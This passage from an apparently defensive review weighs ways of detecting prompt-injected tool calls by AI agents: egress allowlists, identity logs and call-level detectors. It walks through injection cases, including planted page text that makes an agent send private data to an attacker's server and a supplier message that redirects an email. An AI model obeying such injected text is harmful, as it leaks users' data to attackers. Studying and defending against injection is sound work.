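The test may also have been too easy. Li and colleagues split each task's runs between training and testing, so the classifiers were trained on other runs of all three malicious tasks. A classifier could succeed by recognising a familiar task, and might do worse on a new kind of misuse. *Content-Aware Attack Detection in LLM Agent Tool-Call Traffic* (Zavrak, 2026) reports that this kind of overlap greatly inflated results for a detector that reads tool-call records.

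For injected calls, the bigger problem is that the agents pursued a harmful goal from the start. The misuse runs averaged about 22 recorded steps, whereas an injection might change one step in an otherwise ordinary run, or only one argument in that step.

In another experiment in the same paper, eight classifiers sorted 2,101 single steps into 47 types, such as searching, reading a file or running a command. Their accuracy ranged from 35.5% to 46.2%. That is far better than random guessing, but most of the correct answers were for common steps. Even a perfect classifier of this sort would not distinguish Dana's two emails, because emailing Luis and emailing an attacker are the same type of step.

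A sensor's record also depends on where a tool runs. When Claude Code fetched a web page, the capture showed a lookup of the site's name and a download from the site. The model provider ran Claude Code's web searches, so most of the search traffic was between the agent and the provider. An injected search would therefore leave little trace of the sites involved.

### Identifying the agent

Encrypted traffic can also reveal which agent somebody is using. In *Exposing LLM User Privacy via Traffic Fingerprint Analysis*, Zhang, Deng and colleagues (2025) recorded the traffic between users and hosted agents. Their system, AgentPrint, divides the traffic into short periods, counts the packets and bytes in each, and passes the counts to a neural network. An agent that draws a picture, for example, sends a short description, pauses and then transfers a lot of data, while a text conversation produces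 a steadier flow.

AgentPrint distinguished 50 agents with an F1 score, which combines precision and recall, of 0.866 out of 1, and five kinds of behaviour with a score of 0.924. Zhang and colleagues present this as a threat to privacy, since someone who regularly uses a diagnostic agent may be a doctor. In a study with 49 people, their system's top three predictions out of 12 occupational groups included the right one 69.1% of the time, compared with 25% for random guessing.

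A company could use the same method to find agents that its employees run without permission. This would help with injections indirectly, because a company cannot restrict or monitor an agent it doesn't know about. But an injected call comes from an agent the company expects, often doing something it does every day. AgentPrint would correctly identify that Dana's finance assistant was sending an email, but not that injected text had caused it.

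The results may also be better than a company could achieve in practice. Zhang and colleagues wrote prompts to trigger each agent's main function, because an email agent that answers a casual question looks like any chatbot. *A Large-Scale Benchmark and Risk Assessment of Traffic Analysis Attacks* (2026) notes that laboratory results for this kind of analysis may not carry over to real networks, where conditions change. Li and colleagues warn that timing in real deployments may differ from timing in their controlled environments.

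Simple rules about behaviour can fail even at the easier task of finding agents. Canale and Soulis (2026) tested two rules in *Detecting Shadow AI* that used only a computer's processes and connections. Both rules flagged every "behavioural twin", a harmless program that acts like an agent but connects to a service unrelated to AI. Distinguishing twins from agents required identifying that service. A network sensor may be unable to do this, because many AI services share a content delivery network with unrelated sites.

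### Silent Egress and destination allowlists

*Silent Egress* reports the clearest success for network controls. Lan and colleagues planted an instruction in a web page's title, description, main text or links, directing the agent summarising the page to send private data to an attacker's server. The agent sent a request to that server in 423 of 480 runs (88.1%).

In 95% of these successful attacks, the agent's reply looked harmless. The user received the requested summary and no sign that anything else had happened. Lan and colleagues conclude that safety checks would miss these attacks, which follows if the checks read only the reply. The request was plainly visible in the network traffic.

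The researchers then compared defences on the version with instructions in the main text, with 30 runs for each:

| Defence | Runs in which the attacker received a request |
|---|---|
| None | 100% |
| Tags marking web content as untrusted data | 100% |
| System prompt forbidding instructions from web content | 67% |
| Both the tags and the system prompt | 57% |
| Allowlist of permitted domains | 0% |

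The tags and the stricter prompt relied on the model to ignore the attacker, while the allowlist used software to block each request after the model had written it.

Other filters also reduced the rate to zero, but those results are less convincing. One filter blocked web addresses containing words such as "collect", which appeared in the address used in the paper's examples. Another searched outgoing addresses for terms such as "password" and "api_key". It triggered in only 23% of runs, and Lan and colleagues suggest that the model sometimes rewrote the sensitive text. If so, some of the rewritten text should have reached the attacker, but they report that none did. A filter for random-looking strings apparently stopped the agent from even trying, which is odd because the filter runs after the model has written its request. The allowlist result is more convincing because all the attempts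 appear in the data and all of them failed.

The overall success rate is weak evidence about current agents, because the model, Qwen2.5 7B, is small and old, the system prompt was minimal, and the private data was already in the model's input. Lan and colleagues describe the setup as deliberately favourable to the attacker. Models released in 2026 would probably follow far fewer of these instructions. The allowlist's advantage doesn't depend on the model in the same way, because an allowlist blocks requests to a forbidden domain whatever caused them.

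An allowlist has to suit the agent's job and cover every way the agent could make a request. If the harness checks one web tool but the agent can also run shell commands, a command may bypass the check. A firewall around the agent's whole environment can cover requests from both, and it can often read the server's name without decrypting the connection.

The same approach can protect a company's internal systems. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (2026) recommends blocking an agent's outgoing connections by default, including those to private addresses, administrative services and the internal addresses where cloud machines get credentials. Otherwise, because the agent is inside the network, an injected call could reach services that an outsider cannot.

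### Which injected calls network controls can stop

Network controls are most useful when an injected call has to reach a destination the agent doesn't otherwise need. That is true of the attacks in *Silent Egress*, and such controls could also have caught the connection to an outside server in the suspected attack on Cline's build process. The company only needs to know which destinations the agent requires, so it doesn't have to decrypt the traffic or decide whether the model followed an injection. Blocking works better than alerting here because a single request can leak a secret.

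Unusual traffic volume can also reveal an attack without decryption, but only if the data crosses a network the company monitors. In the Copilot Studio case, Microsoft's own services read the records and sent the email, so the customer's network would have carried little or none of that traffic.

When the injected call goes to an approved service, a sensor has to read the call. Decryption makes this possible, but Sohail's test of Suricata showed that a standard set of rules may not cover tool calls, so someone has to write rules for the particular agent. Some of these are simple. If Dana's assistant never needs to create mail-forwarding rules, a gateway can block that tool by name.

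Rules based on tool names can't distinguish between calls to the same tool. Zavrak tested detectors on records of tool calls and found that tool names and response lengths alone gave a score of about 0.64, where 0.5 is chance and 1 is perfect. Adding the content of arguments and responses raised the score above 0.89. For Dana's assistant, a rule allowing email only to colleagues would block the injected message, but also the messages she wants to send to suppliers. A narrower rule could require approval only for the first message to a new address.

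Some injected calls, such as an unrequested change to a supplier's bank details, would pass even a gateway that inspects everything. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* gives the network a smaller role when an attack stays inside an application, such as when an agent fetches another customer's record from a database it is allowed to use. The application has to block such access, as Quarkslab's repaired medical assistant did.

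Other calls never reach the company's network sensors. An MCP server on the same machine as the agent can exchange messages with it through the operating system, so an injected call that deletes local files may create no network traffic. Calls to tools that a provider runs on its own servers also bypass these sensors, as in the ReLeak attacks on Copilot. For these calls, the company depends on records from the harness, the computer or the provider.

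## Surveys and log records: who the logs say acted

When an injected call leaves no trace on the network, an investigator has to start with the receiving service's log to work out who made the call. Two surveys from 2026 suggest that many companies would struggle to do this, although neither included a test of companies' logs. The difficulty depends largely on which account the agent uses, which also affects how well anomaly detection can work.

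### What security staff report

*Identity and Access Gaps in the Age of Autonomous AI* (Baron, 2026), a report from the Cloud Security Alliance, a non-profit industry body, found that 32% of respondents could *very* clearly distinguish AI agents' activity from people's. The other 68% may include people who can tell the two apart fairly well. In March 2026, however, the Alliance announced that 68% of organisations can't clearly distinguish them. Its press release, *More Than Two-Thirds of Organizations Cannot Clearly Distinguish AI Agent from Human* (2026), and the report's own summary both omit the word "very", which makes the result sound worse than it is.

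In the same survey, 69% agreed that they could trace an agent's actions back to their context or to whoever started them, though only 25% agreed strongly. If the same people answered both questions, at least 37% said they could trace an agent's actions but could not very clearly tell them from a person's. These answers are compatible, because an analyst may be able to trace an action after a day's work but not recognise it as an agent's in a log.

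The survey also asked how an agent's identity is typically represented when it acts:

| Identity the agent uses | Share of organisations |
|---|---|
| Application or workload identity | 52% |
| Shared or generic service account | 43% |
| Its own dedicated identity | 36% |
| A human user's identity | 31% |
| Unsure | 12% |

These figures add up to 174%, so respondents could choose several answers. The 43% is therefore the share of organisations that use shared accounts for some agents, not the share of agents that use them. Asked what typically determines an agent's access, only 11% of respondents named a shared account.

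Aembit, which sells identity management for agents, commissioned the survey and helped write the questionnaire. The Cloud Security Alliance analysed the 228 responses, collected online from IT and security professionals in January 2026. An online survey of industry professionals is unlikely to be a random sample, so the margin of error for a random sample of that size, about six percentage points, may not apply. The press release states that 85% of organisations use agents in production, but 18% of respondents reported using no agents, so the two figures can't both be right for the same group.

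The survey's bigger limitation is that it recorded opinions. Researchers could measure attribution directly by giving analysts a log with a known mix of human and agent actions and counting how many the analysts sorted correctly.

Okta's *Global CISO Insights 2026* (2026) reports a lower figure for shared accounts. Of 306 security executives, 21% said they managed agents' access with shared credentials or service accounts with broad permissions. One in four treated agents exactly like human identities, and fewer than half were confident they could identify every agent in their environment. The 21% may be lower than the 43% because Okta asked about broad permissions, or because executives know less about everyday practice than their staff do. Okta sells identity products too. Shared accounts for agents are probably common, but these surveys can't show exactly how common.

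### Three records of one email

Suppose Dana's finance assistant sends the injected email to `desk@example.net`, and the company runs all its agents on one platform, which the mail service knows as `office-agents`. The table shows invented log entries for the same email under three kinds of credential:

| Field | Shared service account | Dana's delegated token | Token naming Dana and the agent |
|---|---|---|---|
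| Time | 14:07:31 | 14:07:31 | 14:07:31 |
| Account | `svc-agents@example.com` | `dana@example.com` | `dana@example.com` |
| Actor | none | none | `finance-assistant-07` |
| Client | `office-agents` | `office-agents` | `office-agents` |
| Action | message sent | message sent | message sent |
| Recipient | `desk@example.net` | `desk@example.net` | `desk@example.net` |

The first entry shows that something on the agent platform sent the email. If twenty agents were running at 14:07, the entry doesn't identify which one sent it or whose task it was working on. tianpan.co (2026), a practitioner's blog, describes the same problem with a deleted production resource, where the log shows the shared account and the response team can't determine which person triggered the deletion. The mail service also can't apply each user's permissions, so the MCP server has to recreate them.

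A shared account can leave it unclear whether an agent acted. *Auditable Claims about AI Agents* (Zhao, 2026) describes a hypothetical case in which a mail gateway records four emails from an agent's account but the agent's own log contains only three. A person could have sent the extra email by hand, the agent could have sent it without logging it, or the log could have lost an entry.

The second entry connects the email to Dana. Its client field also shows that the email came from the agent platform and not her usual mail program. Without that field, the email would look like one she had sent herself. *Identity Management for Agentic AI* (2025) reports that services often log an agent's calls so that they look identical to the user's own. *Five Primitives for Governing Autonomous AI Agents at Runtime* (2026) claims that this happens in every downstream log when an agent uses a person's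 credential. That claim is too strong for a delegated token if the service logs the client, as Salesforce did in the Drift thefts. It is more likely to be true when an agent logs in with Dana's password.

An investigator also can't settle the matter by checking whether Dana was at her desk, because agents often act long after the user's last session, as *AI Identity* (2026) points out.

The third entry identifies both Dana and the particular agent. If the harness keeps traces, the investigator now knows which one to open.

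### How a token comes to name both

The technical basis for the third entry is an internet standard from before the current generation of agents, *OAuth 2.0 Token Exchange* (Jones, 2020), also known as RFC 8693. It distinguishes impersonation from delegation. In impersonation, the agent receives a token that identifies only Dana, and the receiving service can't tell the two apart. In delegation, the agent keeps its own identity and the token shows that it is acting for her. The exchange for a delegation token works as follows:

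1. The harness sends the authorisation server, which issues tokens, one token that represents Dana and another that represents the agent.
2. The authorisation server validates both. Dana's token may contain a `may_act` field that lists who is allowed to act for her.
3. If its policy permits, the server issues a new token that names Dana as the subject and the agent as the actor.
4. The harness attaches the new token to the agent's calls.

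The relevant part of the new token might look like this:

```json
{
  "sub": "dana@example.com",
  "act": { "sub": "finance-assistant-07" }
}
```

The `act` field is called the actor claim. If an MCP server later exchanges this token for one that works at another service, the MCP server becomes the current actor and the finance assistant moves into a second `act` field nested inside the first, so the new token records both actors. Under the standard, services must ignore earlier actors when deciding whether to allow a request, but a monitoring tool could still use them, for instance to look for unusual activity by the finance assistant.

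None of this happens automatically. If the harness sends only Dana's token, the result is impersonation. Even if it sends both tokens, the authorisation server can decline to issue a combined one. The mail service must also copy the actor into its log. If it accepts the combined token but records only the subject, the investigator gets the second entry in the table.

Developers also lack a common format for representing actors. In *OAuth Actor Profile for Delegation*, a draft standard from April, McGuinness (2026) notes that existing specifications don't represent actors consistently across token types. They also have no standard way to indicate what kind of entity an actor is, information a service would need to distinguish AI agents from other software.

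### What standards and platforms ask for

The Model Context Protocol makes authorisation optional. Its *Security Best Practices* gives audit trails as one reason for the rule against forwarding a client's token. If a server forwarded the token, the next service's log could attribute the request to someone other than that server. But the server may still reach that service through a shared account. The protocol's July 2026 authorisation rules do not include token exchange among the standards they build on, so a server could follow the rule against forwarding and still produce the first entry in the table.

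The Internet Engineering Task Force (IETF), which publishes internet standards, is working on rules specifically for agents. One of its working groups adopted a draft called *AI Agent Authentication and Authorization* (Kasselman, Lombardo and colleagues, 2026) and replaced it in September with a new version, known as AIMS. According to Zhao, AIMS requires seven fields in every audit record, including the action an agent requested but not arguments such as the recipient. A log with only those fields would omit the one detail that distinguishes Dana's two emails. AIMS is still a draft, and companies can log more than it requires.

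NIST is at an earlier stage. In February 2026, Booth, Fisher and colleagues proposed a project on applying existing identity standards to agents, in *Accelerating the Adoption of Software and AI Agent Identity and Authorization*, and asked for comments. They want systems to distinguish agents from people, link each agent to a user and link each action to the agent that took it. They also suggest tracking where prompts and input data came from, which is the idea most relevant to injections because it could link the email to `desk@example.net` with the supplier's message. The paper contains proposals and questions but no requirements.

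In a May 2026 white paper with test results on AI tools from other companies, Microsoft explains that most such tools reach SharePoint files with a token that represents both the signed-in user and the application. The information needed for the second entry in the table is therefore available when the call arrives. But the paper lists being able to see what content left the organisation, when, under which user and for what purpose under the heading of a "desired future state", which suggests that customers can't yet count on having all of this.

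Microsoft recommends its own Copilot connectors, whose activity appears in its audit tools, so an organisation can see who accessed which data. Microsoft's paper is partly an argument for buying Copilot, and knowing who accessed a file doesn't explain why. In one of Microsoft's tests, a data loss prevention policy stopped Copilot from processing a sensitive file, but ChatGPT, Gemini and Claude could all read it on the same user's behalf. The policy was set up to block Copilot, so this is not very surprising, but it shows that a rule written for one agent may not cover the others a user has connected.

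### Shared accounts and behavioural baselines

Anomaly detection compares each call with the account's normal activity. When several agents share an account, its normal activity is a mixture of theirs. If agent *i* makes a share *wᵢ* of the calls, and a detection rule *A* wrongly flags a share *Pᵢ(A)* of that agent's benign calls, the false positive rate for the whole account is

P(A) = w₁P₁(A) + w₂P₂(A) + … + wₙPₙ(A)

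One agent with varied work can therefore make a rule useless for all the others. Suppose twenty agents share an account and each makes 100 calls a day. A reporting agent sends the same figures to the same three people and has a legitimate reason to email a new outside address once in 10,000 calls. A sales agent emails 30 new outside addresses a day. The other eighteen never email anyone new. A rule that flags every email to a new outside address would perform as follows:

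| Where the company applies the rule | False positive rate | False alerts |
|---|---|---|
| The reporting agent's own account | 0.01% | about one every 100 days |
| The shared account | 1.5% | about 30 a day |

If an injection makes the reporting agent email an attacker, the alert will almost certainly stand out if the agent has its own account, but under the shared account it is one of 31 alerts that day. Similarly, twenty extra calls would increase the reporting agent's call volume by 20% but the shared account's by only 1%.

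Separate accounts help much less with the sales agent, because an attacker's address could go unnoticed among its 30 new addresses a day whether or not the agent has its own account. Dana's assistant has the same problem to a lesser degree.

If a delegated token has no actor claim, the logs also mix Dana's own emails with her assistant's under her account. Recording the actor lets a company model the assistant separately. An added field can't make the best possible detector worse, but in practice splitting the data leaves less history for each model. If the assistant sends six emails a working day for Dana, a detector would have only about 130 examples after a month. The company could combine data from everyone who uses the same assistant, but the baseline would be less specific.

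*Who Governs the Machine?* (2026) proposes giving every agent a permanent identifier, tied to its model version and configuration, that appears in each log entry. This could prevent some false alerts. When a company upgrades an agent's model, the agent's behavior may change harmlessly, and an analyst who sees the new version in the log can immediately explain the change.

### Does better identity solve the problem?

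The Cloud Security Alliance argues in *Who's Behind That Action?* (2026) that companies should give agents their own identities, limit each agent's access to its task and make every action attributable. This would have benefits besides sharper baselines. If Dana's assistant had an identity that could email only colleagues, the mail service would reject the injected call. The company could also disable a misbehaving assistant alone, whereas disabling the shared account in the example would stop all twenty agents. In the Alliance's survey, 49% of organisations named disabling an agent's identity as a way to limit its access.

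In Okta's survey, half of the companies with "advanced" management of AI identities could revoke an agent's access within minutes, compared with 26% of all companies. This is limited evidence that better identity management speeds up the response, because the result partly follows from Okta's definition of "advanced" as having automated, real-time access controls.

*Identity Management for Agentic AI* expects that proper delegation will let companies trace every action to its origin, meaning the person who authorised it and the agent that carried it out. For an injected call, the origin that matters most is the text that caused it, and no identity field contains that text. In the fullest of the three records, the entries for the email Dana wanted and the injected one would have the same account, actor and client, and would differ only in time and recipient. *Five Primitives* similarly argues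 that knowing which program is calling is "necessary and not sufficient" when the program decides its own actions. A company also needs to know whether the agent may email this recipient or pay this amount.

More detailed identity records could even mislead an investigator. An entry that names Dana and her assistant seems to show everyone responsible, but Dana asked for something else and the entry omits the attacker.

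Supporters of better identity could respond by tying each permission to the specific arguments of a tool call. Zhao describes an invented firm where a signed-in person must approve a grant before the agent sends any external email with an attachment. The grant names the recipient and contains a fingerprint of the attached file. The authorisation server stores the grants and the mail gateway records what the agent sends, so an auditor can compare the two. In one case, the agent's log records that a user clicked to confirm an email, but the authorisation server has no matching grant, so the email broke the policy.

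A similar rule for all of Dana's emails would expose the injected call, because the authorisation server would hold a grant for Luis but none for `desk@example.net`. Nobody would have to recognise the instruction in the supplier's message. If the gateway checked for a grant before delivering each email, it could also block the call. As with capabilities, Dana would have to approve recipients in advance. An injected agent could also request a grant for the attacker's address, and Dana might approve it without looking closely. As Zhao notes, a grant does not show what the approver understood.

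Without grants like these, finding out whose text caused a call usually requires the harness trace, so the trace has to be trustworthy. Zhao cites an experiment on a log that a harness kept about itself, protected by a hash chain. Each entry in the chain contains a fingerprint of the one before, so later changes are visible. The chain revealed none of 28 planted omissions and false entries, because it can't show that an entry was false or missing from the start. A separate log outside the harness revealed all 28.

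This is less of a concern for Dana's assistant, because the attacker controls some of the text the model reads but not the software that writes the log. An agent that can run commands on the same machine is riskier, since an injected call might alter the log or the software that writes it. A gateway's record of the email would then be better evidence that the agent sent it, but the company could still lose the supplier's message that explains why.

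## Tests of detectors that read the calls themselves

A gateway or a harness trace can give a detector the full text of each tool call, which most network sensors and service logs lack. Some detectors compare this text with the agent's past behaviour, and some compare it with the user's request. Others run the agent again with the untrusted text altered and check whether it makes the same call. Software can also track where each argument came from and block calls that break a rule. In published tests, all these methods stop most attacks, but they vary widely in how often they interrupt harmless work.

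### Is the sequence of calls usual?

Liu and colleagues built TraceAegis around the calls that a gateway can record. It learns from normal runs and then checks new ones:

1. It gives each tool a level, based on how early the tool appears in normal runs. Tools on the same level can come in any order.
2. It splits each run into short units that pass through the levels once. If a clinic's assistant looks up a patient's symptoms and then fetches checklists from orthopaedics and psychiatry, the run becomes two units, one for each department.
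3. A language model turns each unit into a rule that links conditions to an action. It then merges similar rules, so that knee pain and arm pain both become reasons for a visit to orthopaedics.
4. When a new run arrives, TraceAegis flags any unit it has not seen before. If all the units are familiar, a language model checks whether the conditions in the matching rules hold.

Liu and colleagues tested TraceAegis on two agents, one that directs patients to clinical departments and one that routes purchase requests at a simulated car manufacturer. For each agent, they generated 1,300 benign traces and 300 abnormal ones. Half of the abnormal traces contained a new sequence of calls, such as one that included a search for sensitive files. The other half had a familiar sequence, but its content made no sense, as when the agent sent a patient with back pain to psychiatry.

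With DeepSeek-V3 as its language model, TraceAegis achieved F1 scores of 0.96 for the clinic and 0.93 for procurement, according to Liu and colleagues' results table. Their text reverses the two scores, but the detailed counts match the table. TraceAegis caught 289 of the 300 abnormal clinic traces and 280 of the 300 abnormal procurement traces. The precision figures imply false positive rates of roughly 3% for the clinic and 7% for procurement.

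The 20 abnormal procurement traces that TraceAegis missed all had a familiar sequence of calls. With a smaller model, Gemma 3 27B, it missed 86 of the 150 abnormal traces with a familiar sequence. An injection that changes only one argument would also leave the sequence familiar, so the overall scores probably overstate how well TraceAegis would catch such an injection. Some of the abnormal traces came from improper user requests, not injected text.

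A technology company tried TraceAegis on an agent that looks for security flaws in software. The agent always works through five stages, from collecting background information to writing a report. In an internal exercise, testers created 140 runs that departed from this workflow, and TraceAegis flagged 132 of them (94%). In one attack, text hidden in a configuration file made the agent write its report before verifying its findings. The exercise is good evidence of high recall, but Liu and colleagues give no false positive rate for it, so we can't tell how many alerts the company's analysts would have to read.

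Fixed workflows suit this method because normal runs soon cover nearly every legitimate sequence, so a new one is a good reason for an alert. An open-ended assistant keeps producing new sequences as its users ask for new things. In *AgentSentry*, Zhang, Xu and colleagues (2026) ran TraceAegis on the varied tasks in AgentDojo, where it interfered with 34% to 36% of the harmless tasks. They were comparing it with their own detector, and AgentDojo may not provide as much normal history as TraceAegis needs. Even so, the rate was several times higher than in the clinic and procurement tests, as one would expect with more varied work.

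For Dana's assistant, checking the sequence of calls would help little. The wanted and injected emails both come from `read_message` followed by `send_email`, which is a familiar unit. If the assistant sent both emails in one run, TraceAegis would split the run into two such units, and neither would look new. The check of conditions could still catch the outside address, but only if Dana's past emails followed a clear rule about recipients, because the gateway has no record of what she asked for this time.

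### Does the call serve the user's request?

A task-alignment check compares each proposed call with the request. Task Shield, which Feiran Jia and colleagues published in 2025, blocks steps that do not fit the user's objective. A simple check of this kind for Dana's assistant would work as follows:

1. The harness holds the assistant's call before running it.
2. It gives Dana's request and the proposed call, but not the supplier's message, to a second language model.
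3. The second model judges whether the call helps to carry out the request.
4. If it does, the harness runs the call. If not, the harness refuses the call and tells the assistant to return to the request.

Withholding the supplier's message from the check makes it harder for the attacker to influence the judgement. Dana asked for an email to Luis, so the check should pass that email and refuse the one to `desk@example.net`.

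When a user asks an agent to handle everything in a message, the check has almost nothing to compare a call with. *AttriGuard* (He, Zhu and colleagues, 2026) describes an intermediate case, in which a user asks an agent to read a web page and email Alice if the page is in English or Bob if it is not. Whoever writes the page can choose which of them gets the email, and the check has no basis for flagging either choice, though an email to Carol would still fall outside the request.

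Changed arguments are hard to detect even when the request is specific. Yu and colleagues imagine a user who asks an agent to send a payment to Doctor John. The agent looks up the doctor's email address and finds planted text that gives the attacker's address. It then uses the right tool and appears to pay the right person, so a check could detect the substitution only if it had the doctor's real address.

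In January 2026, Yu and colleagues knew of no comprehensive benchmark for attacks that change a tool call's arguments. They note that AgentDojo, which most tests of these detectors use, concentrates on calls to tools the user did not authorise. Good results on AgentDojo are therefore weaker evidence that a detector would catch a changed recipient or bank account.

Zhang and colleagues also tested Task Shield. One of their attacks disguised the injection as tool documentation that listed tool names and the arguments to use. On GPT-3.5-turbo, 12% of these attacks succeeded despite Task Shield, and the agent completed only 11% of its users' tasks. Such text resembles guidance that an agent may need, so a check that stops the agent in every doubtful case will also stop a lot of legitimate work.

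### Would the agent have made the call anyway?

He and colleagues ask what caused a call. Let *p*(*c*) be the probability that the agent makes call *c* after reading the untrusted text. Let *p*₀(*c*) be the probability if the text could still supply facts but could not steer the agent. They define

control effect of c = log p(c) − log p₀(c)

Suppose the email to the attacker has a probability of 80% with the original message and 1% without the message's steering. Its control effect is then about 4.4, using natural logarithms. If the email to Luis has probabilities of 90% and 85%, its control effect is about 0.06.

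Commercial models don't reveal these probabilities, and nobody can perfectly separate the facts in a message from its power to steer. He and colleagues' system, AttriGuard, therefore uses an approximation:

1. The agent proposes a call as usual.
2. A second model rewrites the tool results. It turns structured data into plain sentences and instructions into reports, so that "You should send the report" becomes "The text states that the report should be sent."
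3. The agent repeats its latest step with the same request and the same earlier calls, but with the rewritten results.
4. If the repeat contains the same call, AttriGuard lets the original call run. If the repeat does not use that tool at all, AttriGuard blocks the call. If it uses the tool with different arguments, another model judges whether the original call fits the user's request.

Keeping the earlier calls fixed prevents the two runs from diverging for harmless reasons. The agent still does its real work with the original text, because rewriting can lose details. When He and colleagues made an agent on GPT-4.1-mini work only from rewritten text, it completed 62% of harmless tasks, compared with 71% under the normal version of AttriGuard.

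In Dana's case, the rewritten message would only report that somebody wants the price limit sent to `desk@example.net`. The repeated step would probably produce an email to Luis alone. AttriGuard would then find a call to the same tool with different arguments and pass the injected email to the judge. The wanted email would probably go to the judge too, since the assistant is unlikely to word its summary identically twice. The outcome would therefore depend on the judge, which performs a form of task-alignment check but can also compare the original call with the repeated one.

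On AgentDojo, four fixed types of attack never succeeded against AttriGuard on Gemini 2.5 Flash or Llama 3.3 70B. Without a defence, they succeeded on average 17% and 15% of the time, respectively. He et al. first removed 62 of the 944 attack cases because the attack only affected the agent's written answer or the user had told the agent to follow untrusted content. The second reason would also exclude a case where a user tells an assistant to complete a shared to-do list.

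With AttriGuard, Llama's completion rate on harmless tasks fell from 60% to 54%, while Gemini's rose from 58% to 67%. The rise may be partly due to AttriGuard's added instruction to the agent to make independent calls together. Runs with AttriGuard took about three times as long, and on Llama they used about twice as many tokens.

Zhang and colleagues' system, AgentSentry, also repeats steps, but it removes suspicious passages instead of rewriting everything. After each tool result, it works as follows:

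1. The agent proposes its next call, and the harness saves a copy of everything the agent has received so far.
2. The harness runs the model again with a fixed question in place of the user's request. The question asks whether any of the tool results try to control the agent. If some do, the model has to quote them and state which call they would lead to.
3. The harness cuts the quoted passages and repeats both runs. It does not execute any of the calls from these test runs.
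4. If the agent's proposed call disappears once the passages are gone, and so does the call from step 2, AgentSentry treats the proposed call as injected. It also compares results over three successive steps to catch influence that builds up gradually.
5. The agent then continues from the cleaned text.

In Dana's case, the fixed question should expose the instruction to send out the price limit. With that instruction removed, the assistant would email Luis his summary and send nothing to the attacker.

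On 560 attacked office tasks, a version of AgentSentry that stopped the agent blocked every attack, but the agent completed only 55% of the tasks. The full version, which lets the agent continue, also blocked every attack, and the agent completed 92% of the tasks.

### How often the detectors interrupt harmless work

Zhang and colleagues compared all four detectors on AgentDojo with GPT-4o, GPT-3.5-turbo and Qwen3-Max. Each range below spans the results for the three models. The false positive rate is the share of harmless tasks, not calls, in which the detector interfered.

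| Detector | Average attack success rate | False positive rate | Harmless tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| None | 26.2% to 38.9% | 0% | 72.2% to 85.6% |
| TraceAegis | 1.9% to 2.8% | 34.0% to 36.1% | 58.8% to 66.0% |
| Task Shield | 4.9% to 6.7% | 10.3% to 22.7% | 69.1% to 76.3% |
| AttriGuard | 1.5% to 7.3% | 20.6% to 25.8% | 71.1% to 76.3% |
| AgentSentry | 0% | 2.1% to 5.2% | 75.3% to 80.4% |

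AttriGuard did worse here than in He and colleagues' own tests. The cases they excluded and the choice of models and attacks may explain part of the difference. Researchers may also configure a rival's system less well than their own, which they tend to know better. Independent tests would be better evidence for the ranking.

The models in this comparison were old by late 2026. Newer ones follow far fewer injections, but a detector might interrupt just as much of their harmless work. AgentSentry also slowed harmless tasks from an average of 17 seconds to 38 and made them use 2.5 times as many tokens.

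AgentSentry's lowest false positive rate was 2.06%, from two interventions in 97 harmless tasks. At that rate, if the company with a million calls a day spread them over 200,000 tasks, AgentSentry would wrongly interfere with about 4,100 tasks a day. If ten other tasks contained an injected call and it caught all ten, only about one alert in 400 would be real. The test was small, so the 95% confidence interval for the rate runs from 0.25% to 7.25%, or 500 to 14,500 false alerts a day.

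An analyst would not have to read all of these, because AgentSentry cleans the text and lets the agent continue. Many affected users might notice only a delay. But AgentSentry can wrongly remove text that is needed for the task. On Qwen3-Max, the share of harmless tasks completed fell from 85.6% to 80.4%.

### Tracking arguments and applying rules

CaMeL, which Edoardo Debenedetti and colleagues introduced in 2025, applies a policy to tool calls instead of judging whether they look wrong. A model writes a plan from the user's request before it sees any outside text, and software then carries out the plan. When a step needs information from an email or web page, a second model without access to tools extracts it. The software tracks where each value came from and checks every call against rules about which sources may supply which arguments.

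The plan for Dana's request would be to read the thread, summarise the supplier's message and email the summary to Luis. The supplier's message cannot add another email, because the plan is already fixed, or change the recipient, because Dana's request names Luis. The attacker could still get a false statement into the summary, because the summary has to be based on that message.

A company could add a rule that recipients must come from the user's request or the company directory. This rule needs no history of normal calls, and its result doesn't depend on how the attacker words the message. But someone has to choose the right rule. A strict rule would interrupt wanted emails, much as a false alert does, when the recipient's address has to come from the thread.

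Planning in advance also reduces what the agent can do, because many tasks require it to read something before it can decide on the next step. He and colleagues tested CaMeL on AgentDojo, where it stopped every attack:

| Measure | No defence | CaMeL |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless tasks completed, Gemini 2.5 Flash | 57.6% | 38.0% |
| Harmless tasks completed, Llama 3.3 70B | 59.8% | 37.0% |
| Average time per attacked task, Gemini 2.5 Flash | 11 seconds | 165 seconds |
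| Average input per attacked task, Gemini 2.5 Flash | about 12,000 tokens | about 127,000 tokens |

CaMeL was a rival system in this test too, and stronger models may write better plans. The loss also depends on how common attacks are. When every task contained an injection, Gemini completed about 43% of its users' tasks with or without CaMeL. Most real tasks contain no injection, so the figures for harmless tasks better show what a company would lose by using CaMeL.

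IPIGuard, a later system from 2025, relaxes the restriction. It plans the agent's tool use in advance but lets the agent use read-only tools at any time. In He and colleagues' tests on Gemini, the agent completed 74% of harmless tasks under IPIGuard, more than it did without any defence. They attribute this partly to better ordering of the tool calls. However, 3.4% of attacks succeeded, so the extra freedom reduced security somewhat.

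A strict plan should hinder an agent much less if the agent has one narrow job, such as sending a nightly report, because it can do that job without basing any decisions on outside text.

### Longer tasks, changing work and adaptive attackers

Most AgentDojo tasks are short, so Zhang and colleagues also built 96 longer attacks, in which the planted text could stay in the agent's memory or arrive in pieces before taking effect. AgentSentry failed to stop 11 of them. It also interfered with 9 of 96 matching harmless tasks, a higher rate than in the main test.

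In half of these attacks, the agent emailed the right person but included material that the user hadn't asked it to collect. Seven of these 48 attacks succeeded, but 43 did when the researchers switched off the comparison over successive steps. Each call in such an attack can look normal on its own, so a detector that judges calls one at a time can easily miss the attack.

None of these tests followed an agent through months of real work, during which users take on new clients, developers add tools and providers update their models. TraceAegis can learn new sequences, but Liu et al. designed it never to discard a relationship it has learned, so if an unnoticed attack got into the training data, its sequence would count as normal until somebody rebuilt the profile. He et al. warn that updates to the model that rewrites text could affect AttriGuard. AgentSentry's confidence intervals don't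 account for changes to the model or variation between runs.

The tests also include far too few harmless tasks to measure the low false positive rates that a company needs when attacks are rare. For each model, Zhang and colleagues used 949 attacks but only 97 harmless tasks. Even if a detector had raised no false alerts in those 97 tasks, its actual false positive rate could have been as high as about 3%. To show with 95% confidence that the rate is below 0.1%, researchers would need about 3,000 harmless tasks with no false alerts.

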